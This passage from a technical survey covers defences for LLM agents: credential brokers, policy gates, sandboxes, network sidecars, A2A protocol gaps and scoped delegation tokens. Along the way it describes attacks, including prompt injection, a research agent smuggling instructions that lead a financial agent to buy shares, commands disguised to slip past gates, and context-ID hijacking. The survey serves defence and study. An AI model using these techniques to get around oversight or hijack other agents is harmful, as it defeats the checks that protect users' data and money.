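If someone has shut down that part of the network in the meantime, the broker refuses. Otherwise it creates a temporary credential limited to this change, makes the change and signs a record of the outcome. The credential lasts 60 seconds on Kubernetes and 15 minutes on AWS, the minimum AWS allows. AWS can restrict the credential to one firewall group but can't always restrict it to one port, so the broker's proxy checks the port before forwarding the request.

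Revocation is less selective than in CapSeal. Each certificate carries the number of the current revocation period, and increasing that number invalidates every outstanding certificate. This is useful in an emergency, but it also cancels harmless approvals. In tests, the brokers checked the number every five seconds and took at most 5.2 seconds to reject revoked certificates. If they lost contact with the revocation service, they soon refused everything.

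The broker added a median of 28 milliseconds to a Kubernetes change and 137 to a firewall change on AWS. Most of the AWS delay came from checking the current state of the network. He and Yu consider these delays acceptable for infrequent, high-risk changes.

They also ran 1,000 cases in each of nine failure scenarios, including altered requests and reused certificates, and the broker blocked all of them. But each scenario violated a condition the broker was programmed to check. No scenario had an agent bypass the broker and call AWS directly with a credential that an administrator had forgotten to remove. The accompanying proof assumes that no such credential exists. Confirming this in a company with years of accumulated accounts and scripts could be harder than building the broker, and He and Yu acknowledge that the transition is complex.

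### A benchmark that starts with the proposed action

*Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (Jing, 2026) starts with an action the agent has already proposed and tests whether the rest of the system stops it. Most tests of prompt injection start earlier, with a malicious document, and measure whether the agent obeys it.

The design divides the work among four roles. A *planner* drafts an action, a *policy gate* decides on it, an *executor* carries out approved actions, and an *auditor* reviews the log. The gate is ordinary code that applies a policy of 17 rules to allow an action, deny it or ask a human. The planner may be entirely under an attacker's control, but it can't modify the gate, the policy or the log.

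The planner can submit either a shell command or a structured description containing the type of operation, the full file paths and the arguments. Structured descriptions are easier to judge, because a shell command can delete the same file in many ways. It can use a shortened file name, store the path in a variable or call a Python script, and a gate that looks for forbidden text will miss some of these. Each approval is valid once and only for the exact bytes that will run.

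Jing's benchmark has 313 cases. They comprise 54 ordinary operations, 74 openly dangerous ones, 122 disguised attacks, 31 attempts to alter an action after approval or abuse an approval, and 32 faults such as a missing policy file. Five of the disguised attacks could not run on any system, which leaves 117 for the main comparison:

| Configuration | Disguised attacks permitted |
|---|---|
| Direct execution | 98.3% |
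| Gate that checks command text | 43.6% |
| Full four-role design | 30.8% |
| Full design with an operating-system sandbox | 7.7% |

The *sandbox* limits which files a process may write, however the command is phrased. It stopped 27 of the 36 attacks that had got past the gate, but it also made 6 of the 54 ordinary operations (11.1%) fail. The gate had approved all six, but its list of permitted folders didn't match the sandbox's.

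These rates aren't comparable with AgentDojo's, because Jing didn't measure how often an injection would lead a model to propose such actions. Jing assumed the planner was already hostile, as Provos and colleagues did when they analysed OpenSSH's child process.

The 7.7% is also less reliable than it looks, because it comes from a model of the sandbox's behaviour. When Jing ran 94 of the attacks against the real sandbox, 28 didn't test it, for example because the agent refused or the command couldn't run. Of the other 66, five took effect, or 7.6%. The two percentages are almost the same, but the model had also predicted that five of the 94 would work, and none of those five did. One attack that did work deleted a file outside the permitted folder, because the sandbox restricted deletions only on the disk that held the workspace. The model was based on the assumption that a sandbox which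 blocks writing to a file also blocks deleting it.

The headline false-allow rate leaves out the openly dangerous operations. For the deployed design, Jing reports a rate of 23.0%, or 17 of those 74 cases. These may include requests that the gate referred to a human, because the main results count a request for human approval as an approval, on the assumption that an unattended agent might approve its own request. A human who read the requests carefully might have stopped some of them.

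Running the benchmark also exposed four defects that nobody had found by reviewing the design:

- The gate approved a description of an action without checking the file that would run. An attacker could get approval and then swap the file. In an end-to-end test, two of seven variants of this attack deleted a decoy file.
- The gate accepted the same approval more than once.
- A programming error made the gate deny every request of two kinds, which looked like good security in the overall results.
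- The log lost up to 31% of its records when eight processes wrote to it at the same time.

Having the executor check the file's bytes raised the block rate for attacks on approvals from 61.3% to 90.3%. The whole system has only 1,635 lines of Python, so people need to test even a small trusted computing base with attacks as well as read its code.

### Keeping private data out of the permanent record

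A log that nobody can alter stops a compromised agent from hiding its actions, but it also keeps everything written to it for as long as the log exists. *Separating Disclosure from Authorization* (Oswal, 2026) gives the example of a rule about whether an agent may email people outside the company. The rule needs only the part of the recipient's address after the "@", but the simplest implementation sends the full address, the subject and the body to the policy engine, then stores all three permanently.

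Oswal therefore classifies each field of an action separately:

| Kind of field | What the policy engine receives | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Useful for decisions and not identifying | The original value | The number of attachments |
| Useful for decisions but identifying | A less specific value | The domain of an email address; whether a payee is on an approved list |
| Not needed for decisions | Nothing | The text of an email |

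In Oswal's reference set of 19 fields, 11 reach the policy engine unchanged, six reach it in a less specific form and two are withheld. Any unclassified field is also withheld.

An auditor must still be able to verify from the log what the agent did. Before removing anything, software running beside the agent computes a *digest* of the full parameters, a short code that would almost certainly change if any parameter changed. The log stores this digest. An auditor who obtains the original email from the company's mail system can compute its digest and check that it matches the logged one. Because the digest doesn't depend on the classification, the company can reclassify a field later without invalidating old entries.

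Someone with the log can also use a digest to check guesses. If a payment has no memo and only a few plausible payees and amounts, they could compute the digest of each combination until one matched. A long email would be far harder to guess. Including a secret random value in the digest's input would prevent this attack, but Oswal's formula doesn't have one.

Making data less specific can fail too. An early version of Oswal's software replaced identifiers in file paths, but it recognised only standard formats, so it passed on `patient-record-778812` in full. The corrected version drops the last part of the path. This means that rules can't refer to particular file names, but the software doesn't have to recognise every form an identifier can take.

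Denying unapproved actions by default doesn't prevent this kind of leak. If an administrator reclassifies the subject line as useful for decisions, the subject of every later email will go to the policy engine, and no denied request will draw attention to the change. Oswal proposes letting each workload set its own upper limit on what it discloses, which the central settings can tighten but not loosen.

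Oswal's mediator only permits or refuses an action that the agent then carries out itself, so the design has to trust the software beside the agent to report the correct digest. A broker that sends the email already has the address and the text, so it can compute the digest without relying on the agent, then discard the text instead of logging it. But this broker handles everyone's private data, which makes it a more attractive target.

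### When the broker approves the wrong thing

A broker can enforce its policy perfectly and still allow a harmful request. For example, the format check in CapSeal confirms that a chat request contains text, but not that the text is free of passwords. If the destination were a public message board, a valid request could publish the contents of the owner's mailbox.

He and Yu leave this problem to the service that issues certificates. He and Yu (2026), in *Sovereign Assurance Boundary*, describe how it works. The service turns an agent's proposal into a precise contract and attaches evidence, such as system measurements and the report of an outage. It then scores the possible consequences with a weighted sum:

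*risk = αB + βP + γD + δI + ηU*

Here *B* is how many systems the change affects, *P* the additional privileges it needs, *D* the sensitivity of the data, *I* how hard the change is to reverse, and *U* the uncertainty of the evidence. The Greek letters are weights that security engineers set by replaying past incidents. A higher score can lead to stricter checks, such as a human signature valid only for this contract and this evidence. In one example, an agent asks to open a remote-login port to the whole internet, and the service rejects the request.

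The score helps with actions that look dangerous, but it is less useful when an attacker can make such an action look justified. He and Yu acknowledge that a compromised but authorised source can supply false evidence with a valid signature. If the outage report is fabricated, the service may approve an unnecessary firewall change, and the broker will execute it because the certificate is genuine. They also warn that individually reasonable changes can be dangerous together. For example, an agent might open a firewall, give an account more privileges and then export diagnostic logs. The formula scores one contract at a time, so other rules would have to catch the combination.

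A language model acting as the broker could judge purposes and combinations that fixed rules miss, but in a similar test, three models let through most of the disguised attacks. Jing told the models to require explicit approval before any dangerous action, then asked them to judge 150 cases five times each. By majority vote, Claude Opus 5 let through 89.8% of the disguised attacks, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash 94.9% and GPT-6 Astra all of them.

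The scoring exaggerates this failure because Jing counted a request for approval as permission, as in the main results, even though the models had been told to seek approval. GPT-6 Astra asked for approval in about a third of its answers across all cases. The models' inconsistency is stronger evidence against relying on one. Even with the setting that minimises randomness, all five answers agreed in only 49% to 71% of cases, depending on the model. An attacker who can resubmit a rejected request would benefit from this inconsistency.

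Adding a second agent as the approver doesn't necessarily help. Separation of duties works in an office partly because employees can't approve their own requests. Jing cites a warning from an industry analysis that agents can approve their own requests indirectly by routing them through one another. He and Yu let models vote on a proposal but don't trust any single model. Ordinary code verifies the votes and applies the policy, and a model's vote can't override a rule. The votes add less protection if the models are similar, because one misleading report may fool them all.

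### Attacks on the broker itself

Bypassing some brokers and policy checks is easier than tricking them into approving a harmful request. Zou, Guo and colleagues (2026) point out in *AgentKernel* that many tools for controlling agents run in the same process as the agent. Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit is one example, and its documentation says that it doesn't provide operating-system-level isolation. Malicious code that an agent runs inside that process might disable the check or read its secrets. CapSeal avoids this by running the broker as a separate process.

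Running the check in a separate process isn't enough if it covers only a tool's declared behavior. The agent may call a permitted tool with harmless-looking arguments, and the tool may start another program that does something else. Zou and colleagues propose linking each permission to the requests that the tool and any programs it starts actually make to the operating system.

Jing accidentally discovered a forgotten route to the live installation through an administrative network share. Jing had moved the attacks to a copy of the system for a test without the sandbox, but two attack commands still went through the share and deleted a protected file on the live installation. A check built into the test detected the change, and Jing restored the file and excluded such commands from later runs.

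Taking over the broker itself would be worse, because the broker holds all the credentials that separation was meant to keep away from agents. CapSeal doesn't defend against an attacker with full control of the machine, who could read the keys from the broker's memory. He and Yu's broker can assume powerful administrative roles, and its security also depends on its database, the signing keys and the cloud provider. Compromising one agent that holds one key may do less damage than compromising a broker that serves a whole company. Separate brokers for payments, email and cloud administration would limit that damage, but administrators would have more software to maintain.

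An attacker can compromise a broker through the software it is built from. In *CapSeal*, Jin and colleagues cite recent supply-chain compromises of axios, a library for making web requests, and LiteLLM, which can serve as an *AI gateway*. Such a gateway passes an organisation's requests to several model providers and may hold the keys for all of them. Malicious code in the gateway could take the keys directly, without a prompt injection or a request that the policy could refuse. The paper gives no details of either incident, so it doesn't establish what the attackers obtained. Even so, a broker isn't necessarily safe just because no agent can read its memory. CapSeal and the design by He and Yu both assume an uncompromised broker, and Jing explicitly excludes supply-chain attacks.

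A broker can also fail, and if every change has to go through it, its failure blocks every agent. For this reason, He and Yu recommend running several copies of the broker and keeping emergency credentials for human operators where agents can't reach them. Those credentials are another route around the broker, so the company has to protect and monitor them separately.

### Brokers and matchmakers

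*Middle-Agents for the Internet* (Decker, Sycara and Williamson, 1997) addresses how agents can find suitable partners in a large, changing network. A *matchmaker* keeps a directory of services, much like the yellow pages, which a requester uses to find a provider and contact it directly. A *broker* handles both the advertisements and the requests, and stays between the two parties.

In initial experiments, Decker and colleagues found that systems with brokers were more vulnerable to certain failures than systems with matchmakers, but adapted faster when providers were joining and leaving rapidly. Brokers could also meet some privacy needs that matchmakers couldn't. For example, a requester and a provider that communicate only through a broker don't have to reveal their identities to each other, although the broker learns about both.

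Decker and colleagues studied how the choice between a matchmaker and a broker affects load and reliability. The same choice arises when protecting credentials from hijacked language models. A service that gives an agent a temporary key and has no further involvement works like a matchmaker. The agent can keep working if the service fails, but the service can't inspect each later call or prevent the agent from revealing the key. A broker that carries out every action itself can do both, but it is a single point of failure.

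### Why enforce the boundary in the network?

A broker controls only the requests that reach it. *Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (Tran, Dhesi and colleagues, 2026) proposes using the network to make sure that all of an agent's requests go through a checkpoint. Each agent has a separate program next to it, called a *sidecar*. Every message to another agent and every call to an outside service passes through the sidecar, which can allow, edit or deny the request, or ask the user. A *control plane* writes the rules and distributes them to the sidecars. It runs in a protected part of the company's systems, so an agent can't change the rules.

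The design borrows from Ethane, a 2007 system for company networks in which a central controller set the policy and simple switches enforced it. Ethane's designers argued that a network policy works only if all traffic passes through the point of enforcement. Tran and colleagues also adopt the idea of "off by default" networks, so an agent starts without permission to contact anyone. For each task, the control plane can give it a capability that specifies a destination, a type of data and a purpose.

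Tran and colleagues argue that this approach is compatible with the *end-to-end argument*, a principle of network design, despite its usual summary as "keep the network dumb". On their reading, the principle is that a function belongs where it can be performed completely. A file transfer program can check that a whole file arrived, so the check belongs in that program and not in the network. But an agent that an attacker has hijacked can't be relied on to block its own leaks, so that check belongs outside the agent.

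Network enforcement would help with the forgotten AWS credential. The agent might still have the key, but it couldn't send a request to AWS unless the sidecar allowed that destination. The sidecar also doesn't depend on which model or framework the agent uses, which matters to a company that buys agents from several vendors.

Simple rules about destinations can't stop an agent from sending too much data to an approved service, so the sidecar passes some requests to a second component, which considers the user's intent, the task and the sensitivity of the data. This component may use a language model, and some of its information comes from the agent, so an attacker who controls the agent could describe a harmful transfer as part of the user's task. Tran and colleagues acknowledge this weakness and note that the sidecar can't control data once it has left the company. They present a reference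 design without measurements, so its error rate and cost are unknown.

The design covers only what agents send. Checking what they receive is harder, because the sidecar would need information that senders may falsify or omit. Fixed rules also work best when the company knows in advance which agents will run and whom they will contact. But an agent may start another agent during a task, and the control plane then has to decide how much of the first agent's authority the new one should get.

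## What goes wrong when an agent is both requester and provider?

A pump manufacturer's agent might take orders from customers' agents and buy parts from suppliers' agents. This makes it a dual-role agent, a provider to the customers and a requester to the suppliers. If it does both jobs in one context, what a customer writes can influence what it buys, and its replies to suppliers can draw on all the customer information it has.

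Suppose a customer orders 200 pumps. Each pump needs two bearings, which normally cost the manufacturer about €9 apiece. The customer's message says that all bearings must come from a particular supplier, which charges €30. If the agent complies, the 400 bearings cost about €8,400 more than usual. The customer may have a good technical reason for the request, or may secretly own the supplier. Either way, the agent is a confused deputy, because it has spent the manufacturer's money on the instructions of someone with no authority over that money.

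A supplier can also exploit the same agent. It might reply that it can confirm the bearings only if it knows who the pumps are for, where they will run and what they sell for. The agent has all of this in its context. A supplier that learns the price of the pumps can estimate how much more the manufacturer could pay, and one that learns the customer's name can offer to sell spare parts directly to that customer.

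Customers often specify components and suppliers often ask about the intended use, so neither message looks like an attack. If the agent has long-term memory, the customer's preference for one supplier could also affect purchases for everyone else.

### Two agents and a broker

The manufacturer can divide the work like this:

```
 customers' agents            suppliers' agents
         |                            |
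    order agent               purchasing agent
         |                            |
         +---------- broker ----------+
                       |
                 bank account
```

Both of the manufacturer's agents are exposed agents, because both read messages from outsiders. The boundary has to separate outsiders from private data, as it did for the email assistant, and also keep two groups of outsiders from influencing each other's business.

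The broker is ordinary code. When the order agent accepts the order, the broker gives the purchasing agent only a part number (bearing B-204), a quantity (400 pieces) and a price ceiling (€12 each). The purchasing agent collects quotes and proposes a purchase. The broker pays only after checking that the supplier is on an approved list, the part and quantity match an open request, and the price is within the ceiling. It gives the order agent only a delivery date to pass on to the customer.

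| Component | May read | May do | Remaining risk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Order agent | Customers' messages, customer records, product catalogue | Quote for pumps, accept orders | A customer places a false order or gets at another customer's data |
| Broker | Accepted orders, parts lists, approved suppliers, proposed purchases | Pass on the three values, pay for purchases within the limits | A wrong price list or a bug lets through a bad purchase |
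| Purchasing agent | The three values, suppliers' messages | Ask for quotes, propose a purchase | A supplier finds out the ceiling or talks the agent into a poor deal |

The broker should take the ceiling from the manufacturer's price list and calculate the quantity from the number of pumps. If the order agent supplied these values, a customer might persuade it to set the ceiling at €30.

The purchasing agent never receives the customer's name, so a supplier can no longer get it from that agent. But the supplier may be able to get the ceiling, and then quote €11.99 for a bearing it would have sold for €9. On 400 bearings, the manufacturer would pay almost €1,200 more. The broker could keep the ceiling to itself and only accept or reject each quote. It would also have to limit the number of quotes from each supplier, because a supplier with unlimited attempts would find the ceiling.

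The part number can also reveal information about a customer. If only one local company runs pumps with a certain corrosion-proof bearing, the supplier can infer from an order for 400 of them that this company is expanding. The manufacturer could combine several customers' needs into one purchase, though some customers would then wait longer. The three values also can't express a genuine special requirement, such as a food-safe lubricant, unless the manufacturer gives that version its own part number.

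### How A2A lets an agent take either role

The *Agent2Agent protocol* (A2A) is an open standard for requests between agents, which may have different owners. Google introduced it in April 2025 and transferred it to the Linux Foundation that June. Version 1.0.0 came out in March 2026, according to *Agent Identity and Task-Based Access Control*, a post from AGNTCY, an open-source project that builds identity software for agents.

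The *Agent2Agent (A2A) Protocol Specification* defines a *client* as an application or agent that makes a request, and a *remote agent*, or server, as one that processes it. These roles describe the two sides of an exchange, so the same agent can be a remote agent when it takes a customer's order for pumps and a client when it asks a supplier for a quote. Neither side sees the other's reasoning, memory or tools.

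A client learns about a remote agent from its *Agent Card*, a file that lists the agent's identity, skills, address and login requirements. Agents can publish their cards at a standard web address. *A2A v1.0*, a guide for developers (Ghumare, 2026), also describes an optional *extended card*, which a server gives only to callers who have proved their identity. The pump manufacturer's public card might list a quote service open to anyone, while its extended card includes instructions for registered distributors to order at trade prices. The order agent would still have to check each trade order, because a caller can ask for a skill without seeing the card that lists it. The purchasing agent only makes requests, so it doesn't need a card.

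When the client sends a message, the remote agent can answer immediately or open a *task*, which has its own identifier and a state such as "working" or "completed". A *context* identifier groups related tasks, such as an order and a later change to it. The remote agent can pause a task to ask for more information or for authorisation. If the client is working on a task for someone else, it can pause that task too and pass the request for authorisation up the chain until it reaches someone who can decide.

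MuleSoft's *Using A2A Protocol in Agent Networks*, the documentation for one commercial product, describes how each intermediate agent creates a new context and task identifier for the requests it receives. The customer's order and the purchase of bearings would therefore be separate conversations under A2A. But a dual-role agent can still put both into the same model's context.

### Eleven gaps in the specification

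*A2ABREAK* (Lotfi, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) looked for attacks that remain possible when all parties obey every mandatory and recommended rule in version 1.0.0 of A2A and switch on every optional safeguard, such as signed Agent Cards. An attack counted as a vulnerability only if it broke a security goal stated in the specification and no rule prevented it. Developers can still add protections that the specification doesn't mention, so the findings don't mean that every A2A product is open to attack.

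The researchers used language models to turn the specification into 929 formal statements. Of these, 283 described how an interaction moves from one state to another, and the researchers combined them into a *finite-state machine*, a map of the states and the permitted moves between them. It has 37 states and 76 transitions, from discovering an agent to ending a task. A model then searched the map for attacks, and a second step checked each attack against the specification.

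Five searches produced 17 candidates, of which the automated check accepted 16. Three of the researchers reviewed these 16 by hand and found 11 real vulnerabilities, one duplicate and four attacks that existing rules already prevented. Excluding the duplicate, 11 of 15 were correct, a precision of 73.3%. The paper also reports an F1 score of 84.6%, which combines precision with the share of real vulnerabilities found. That score implies a share of 100%, but this can only mean that the automated check didn't discard any real vulnerabilities, because nobody knows how many the searches missed.

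For comparison, Claude Opus 4.6 searched the specification twice without the map and proposed nine attacks. The researchers rejected all nine, mostly because the specification already prohibited a step in the attack. The map therefore seems to help, although two searches are a small sample.

The 11 vulnerabilities affect most stages of a task. Some can occur only because agents take both roles. For example, a supplier's agent might pass part of a job back to the manufacturer whose order it is filling, so that each waits for the other. Another finding is that A2A sets no time limit on a paused task, so both agents could wait forever.

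### Three missing safeguards

A2A ties each task to the client that created it, but contexts have no owner. Suppose one of the pump manufacturer's customers learns the context identifier of a competitor's conversation with the order agent. That customer can then send a request with the identifier, and the order agent may answer using the competitor's history, including its discounts. The new messages also become part of the history, so they can affect the competitor's next order. A long random identifier would be hard to guess, but people don't usually guard identifiers as carefully as passwords, and identifiers may turn up in logs.

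Separating ordering from purchasing doesn't prevent this attack, because both customers deal with the same order agent. Lotfi and colleagues propose that the server record who created each context and reject everyone else, unless the owner has agreed to share it. This check is missing from the specification, and amit-raut had earlier reported it missing from version 0.3.25 of A2A's Python software too, in the proposed change *fix(security): SSRF via AgentCard URL and context ID Injection*.

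The second gap is that A2A establishes identity separately for each connection, so an agent knows which agent contacted it but not who started the chain. Suppose the manufacturer's dual-role agent orders bearings from a dishonest supplier, which hires a laboratory to test them. The laboratory's agent needs the technical requirements in the customer's document store, so it asks for authorisation. The request travels back through the supplier and the manufacturer to the customer, where it appears to come from the manufacturer. The customer can't tell from the protocol which company wants access, or whether the supplier invented the request. If the customer sends a password back along the chain, the supplier can keep a copy.

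Ghumare says credentials should instead travel through a separate channel controlled by the agent that needs them, so that agents in between can't read them. Lotfi and colleagues reply in effect that the customer can't do this reliably, because the protocol doesn't identify that agent. They want each request for authorisation to include a signed record of the whole chain. In the redesigned system, the broker has no field for such a request, so the request would stop at the broker and a person would have to deal with it.

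A third missing safeguard is a way to verify a supplier's skills before the purchasing agent chooses it. Agents describe their own skills in their Agent Cards, and A2A has no way to check these descriptions. A signature on the card confirms who published it, but a dishonest company can sign a card that falsely offers precision machining. A client that believes the card might send the company confidential drawings and receive made-up test results. Lotfi and colleagues suggest that an independent organisation could certify skills, though a certificate wouldn't guarantee how the agent behaves on a particular job. The pump manufacturer's list of approved suppliers already provides much of the same protection, but it excludes new suppliers until someone has vetted them.

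For each of these three gaps, the researchers built a small mathematical model and had a program search it for attacks. The program found an attack in each model with A2A's existing protections, but none after the researchers added the missing safeguard. They left attacks on running software to future work.

Lotfi and colleagues reported the first two gaps, which they consider the most severe, to A2A's maintainers and proposed repairs. They say the project's Technical Steering Committee has responded and is working with them to address the issues in the specification. They don't describe the committee's reply in detail, so it isn't clear which repairs it will adopt.

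Some of the 11 findings may reflect deliberate omissions. Lotfi and colleagues don't accept a vague statement that something is up to implementers as proof that A2A's designers left it out on purpose. AGNTCY takes a more charitable view of how authorisation is handled. The protocol defines how an agent asks for permission, and the current draft explicitly leaves the scope, lifetime and revocation of that permission to others. A protocol for many industries could hardly define every permission in advance. But no single company can prevent identity from being lost along a chain, because every agent in the chain has to pass on the same information. The case for a common rule is therefore stronger for preserving identity than for checking skills, which a buyer can do alone.

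### When the provider starts giving instructions

Normally, the requester sends a task and the provider carries it out. But the provider may also ask questions along the way, and the requester's model reads them in the same context as its own instructions. Unit 42, the threat research team at Palo Alto Networks, showed how a malicious provider can use this to reverse the roles and direct the requester. Unit 42 calls the technique *agent session smuggling*.

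The team built two agents: a financial assistant that had access to a user's investments and could buy shares, and a malicious research assistant. In the first demonstration, the user asked for news about the AI market and the financial assistant passed the request on. Before answering, the research assistant asked a series of harmless-looking questions, and the financial assistant's replies revealed its standing instructions, its tools and the user's earlier conversation. In the second demonstration, the research assistant returned extra instructions, and the financial assistant bought ten shares that the user hadn't asked for.

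Both times, the research assistant eventually supplied the news. The developers' screen showed the exchanges in between, but a typical chat window would have shown the user only the final summary.

These demonstrations show that the attack can work, but not how often it does. The second also assumes that the attacker already knows which tools the financial assistant has. Palo Alto Networks had not seen the technique in real attacks. The company doesn't consider this a flaw in A2A, because any protocol that lets agents hold long conversations has the same weakness.

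Palo Alto Networks' recommended defences include comparing each message from the provider with the user's original request and ending the conversation if it strays. This might catch an instruction to buy shares in a conversation about news. It would be less useful against the pump manufacturer's supplier, whose questions about where the bearings will run are on topic. Signed Agent Cards expose impostors but don't help if a genuine supplier is dishonest. The company considers human approval the most effective defence, provided the request for approval appears somewhere the model can't influence.

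In the redesigned system, a supplier that asks the same questions can learn only the three values and whatever other suppliers have told the purchasing agent. If the supplier tells the purchasing agent to buy motors as well, the broker refuses because no order needs them. But the supplier may still persuade the purchasing agent to recommend its quote of €11.99 over a rival's €9. To prevent that, the broker could receive the quotes directly and compare the prices.

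### Separate identities and memory for each role

In *DelegateEval*, a proposed framework for evaluating agents that serve outside clients, Li, Lu and colleagues (2026) accept that one system can be both its owner's assistant and a provider to others, but they want it to keep separate identities, materials, permissions and records for each role. For instance, a software engineer's client can ask for changes to the code it ordered, but cannot authorise the agent to read the engineer's email or permanently change how the engineer works.

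By the same rule, a pump customer may change its own order but not the list of approved suppliers. Li and colleagues also distinguish permission to use a client's material for the current task from permission to keep it for later tasks or to train a model on it. For example, the order agent could use a customer's drawings to prepare a quote but would then have to delete them. The framework is only a proposal so far, with no experiments on how well agents keep their roles apart.

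With separate identities, the manufacturer's order agent and purchasing agent log in with different credentials, so an attacker who takes over the order agent can't contact suppliers as the purchasing agent. The two agents also need separate memories, or the customer's remark about its favourite supplier could reach the purchasing agent through shared notes. The order agent needs a separate memory for each customer, and the purchasing agent needs one for each supplier so that it can't reveal one supplier's quote to another.

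Each new identity takes work to maintain. AGNTCY points out that someone usually has to register every agent with every partner company and manage a secret for each registration. With five purchasing agents and 30 suppliers, that makes 150 registrations. A draft internet standard would let an agent identify itself with a web address where partners can find its public keys, so they wouldn't have to register it beforehand.

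### Tokens that name the user and the agent

With separate logins, a supplier can tell which agent is calling, but not on whose behalf. Many web services use OAuth, a standard that lets a program act for a user with a limited-access token instead of the user's password. An extension called *token exchange*, or RFC 8693, lets a program trade one token for another that it can use with the next service. As Muruaga explains in *Bounded Agents* (2026), the new token can record a chain of acting parties and can restrict who may act on whose behalf.

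AGNTCY sketches a token that names the user and two agents and permits one action on one task. For the purchase of bearings, it might contain:

```
user:      purchasing manager
agent:     purchasing agent
task:      purchase 5831
may do:    buy 400 of bearing B-204
key:       held by the purchasing agent
expires:   in one hour
```

The agent must prove it holds the key each time it uses the token, so a supplier that copies the token can't use it. AGNTCY offers its version as an illustration and doesn't issue such tokens yet. An early draft on the website of the IETF, an internet standards body, would apply a related kind of token to A2A.

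The customer's name doesn't belong in this token. The customer ordered pumps, but the purchasing manager has the authority to spend the manufacturer's money, so the purchase begins a new delegation chain. A single chain from the customer to the supplier would misstate the source of that authority and reveal the customer to the supplier. The broker can record which order each purchase belongs to, so an auditor can connect them later.

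The laboratory's request for documents is different because only the customer can grant it. A token that named the customer and every agent in the chain would show the document store who was asking and for whom, but it would also reveal the customer's identity to the laboratory and possibly the supplier. The manufacturer has to choose between an accurate record of authority and its customer's privacy, or ask the customer to deal with the laboratory directly.

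A valid token also can't prove that an agent followed its instructions. *When Agentic Trust Crosses Organizational Boundaries* (Li and Xia, 2026) describes a provider that receives an authenticated request from a company's purchasing agent to renew a cloud service. The provider can't see what the employee asked the agent to do, what limits the agent had, or whether an injection changed the task on the way. The token would look the same if a supplier had hijacked the agent. The employee's company could send a log, but it also controls that log.

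A2A makes narrow permissions harder to enforce because a request has no field for the skill being requested, so the receiving agent has to infer it from the text. A rule that one caller may ask for quotes but not place orders therefore depends on how a model interprets the message. AGNTCY proposes that clients declare the operation in a separate field. The declaration could only narrow the client's existing permissions, since otherwise a client could gain authority by claiming it.

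### Authority that can only shrink

Recording a delegation chain doesn't limit what each agent in it may do. Muruaga proposes a system in which authority can stay the same or shrink at each step but never grow. An agent's *scope* has four parts: the resources *R* it may use, the types of action *A* it may take, the classes of data *D* it may handle, and the combinations of actions *X* that it may not perform in one session. When one party delegates to another, a program outside the model combines the delegator's scope with the limits of the new role:

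*S₁ ⊓ S₂ = (R₁ ∩ R₂, A₁ ∩ A₂, D₁ ∩ D₂, X₁ ∪ X₂)*

The new agent gets only the resources, actions and data that appear in both scopes, and all the prohibitions that appear in either. For the pump manufacturer, this might give:

| | Manager's grant | Limits of the purchasing role | Purchasing agent's scope |
|---|---|---|---|
| Resources | Bearings, seals, motors | Bearings, seals, paint | Bearings, seals |
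| Actions | Ask for quotes, buy, cancel | Ask for quotes, buy | Ask for quotes, buy |
| Data | Prices, stock levels | Prices, supplier records | Prices |
| Forbidden combinations | Change a supplier's bank details and buy | Read customer data and message a supplier | Both |

If the purchasing agent starts a helper to collect quotes, the program repeats the calculation, so the helper can't get access to motors. The budget also passes down the chain. If the manager permits two purchases and the purchasing agent has already made one, the helper can make at most one more. Muruaga proves that the resources an agent can reach are always a subset of those its delegator can reach. The two sets can be equal, so a designer who passes on everything at each step gains no protection.

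The rule against reading customer data and messaging a supplier in one session would have stopped the original agent from answering the supplier's questions. But that agent had to do both to fill an order, so the rule would also have stopped its normal work. The rule becomes practical only after the manufacturer has split the roles. It also applies only within a single session, and in one of Muruaga's own tests, an attack got through by reading data in one session and sending it in the next. This is another reason to keep the two agents' memories separate.

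Muruaga used AgentDojo and InjecAgent, another set of injection tests, to check whether the system would block an attacker's chosen action. In both, the action was submitted directly, as if the injection had already worked.

| Attack | Success without the system | Success with it |
|---|---|---|
| InjecAgent, data theft | 100% | 0% |
| The same, with one forbidden pair missing | 100% | 39.9% |
| InjecAgent, direct harm | 100% | 60.4% |
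| AgentDojo, sending data or money out | 75–100% | 0% |
| AgentDojo, destruction | 38.6% | 4.0% |
| AgentDojo, manipulation | 90.5% | 12.1% |

The system was best at stopping attacks that need two steps, such as reading a file and then sending it. It was much worse at stopping a single harmful action within the agent's scope. The second row shows how much the system depends on a complete list of forbidden combinations, which people have to write for each kind of work.

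The protection also reduced the share of AgentDojo tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed while under attack. It fell by 13.9 percentage points when the system refused every action that needed approval, and by 8.6 points when the test simulated a person approving those actions.

These benchmarks give an agent tools but don't have it delegate to other agents, so they provide little evidence about delegation chains. For those, Muruaga relies on the proof, which nobody has yet checked by machine, and on 99 scripted scenarios with chains of two to eight steps. All 99 came out as expected, but Muruaga wrote both the scenarios and the system. Progent, which checks tool calls against rules, also stopped every attack in the AgentDojo tests where it could be compared with Muruaga's system, with about the same effect on usefulness. Shrinking authority along a chain may still be valuable, but those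 tests couldn't measure that.

Muruaga's system checks the type of an action but not all of its details, so it treats an order for 4,000 bearings the same as an order for 400. The broker still has to check the quantity and the price. Every step also has to pass through a gateway that enforces the scope, and the manufacturer can install one for its own agents but not inside a supplier's company. Once the supplier's agent hires a laboratory, the manufacturer depends on the supplier to pass on less authority than it received. Tokens that work only for one service and one key-holder reduce this dependence, because the service that receives a token can check both restrictions.

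A dishonest company could also cheat the manufacturer within all these limits by acting as both customer and supplier. It orders 200 pumps through one agent, sells the manufacturer 400 bearings at €11.99 through another, and then cancels the pumps. The two agents exchange no free text, the token names the right manager, and the purchase is within the purchasing agent's scope. The manufacturer could protect itself by having the broker wait for a deposit before buying parts.

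## How do attacks cross between separated agents in experiments?

The pump manufacturer's broker accepts only a part number, a quantity and a price, but in most of the multi-agent systems that researchers have attacked, the agents exchange ordinary text. An agent that reads something malicious can therefore pass it on as a request or a report, and the receiving agent has little reason to distrust a message from another agent in the same system.

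Such systems often divide *work* among specialised agents, such as reading files or writing code, without dividing *authority*. Dividing authority means limiting what each agent can bring about, including by asking the others. Suppose the email assistant's exposed agent can't send mail but can ask the trusted agent to send any message to anyone. An attacker who controls the exposed agent can then still send any message through the trusted agent. The split adds security only if something refuses some of those requests.

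The OpenClaw experiment didn't test how attacks cross between separated agents, because none of its attacks was designed to enlist a second agent. Several other groups have written attacks that do.

### A false error report

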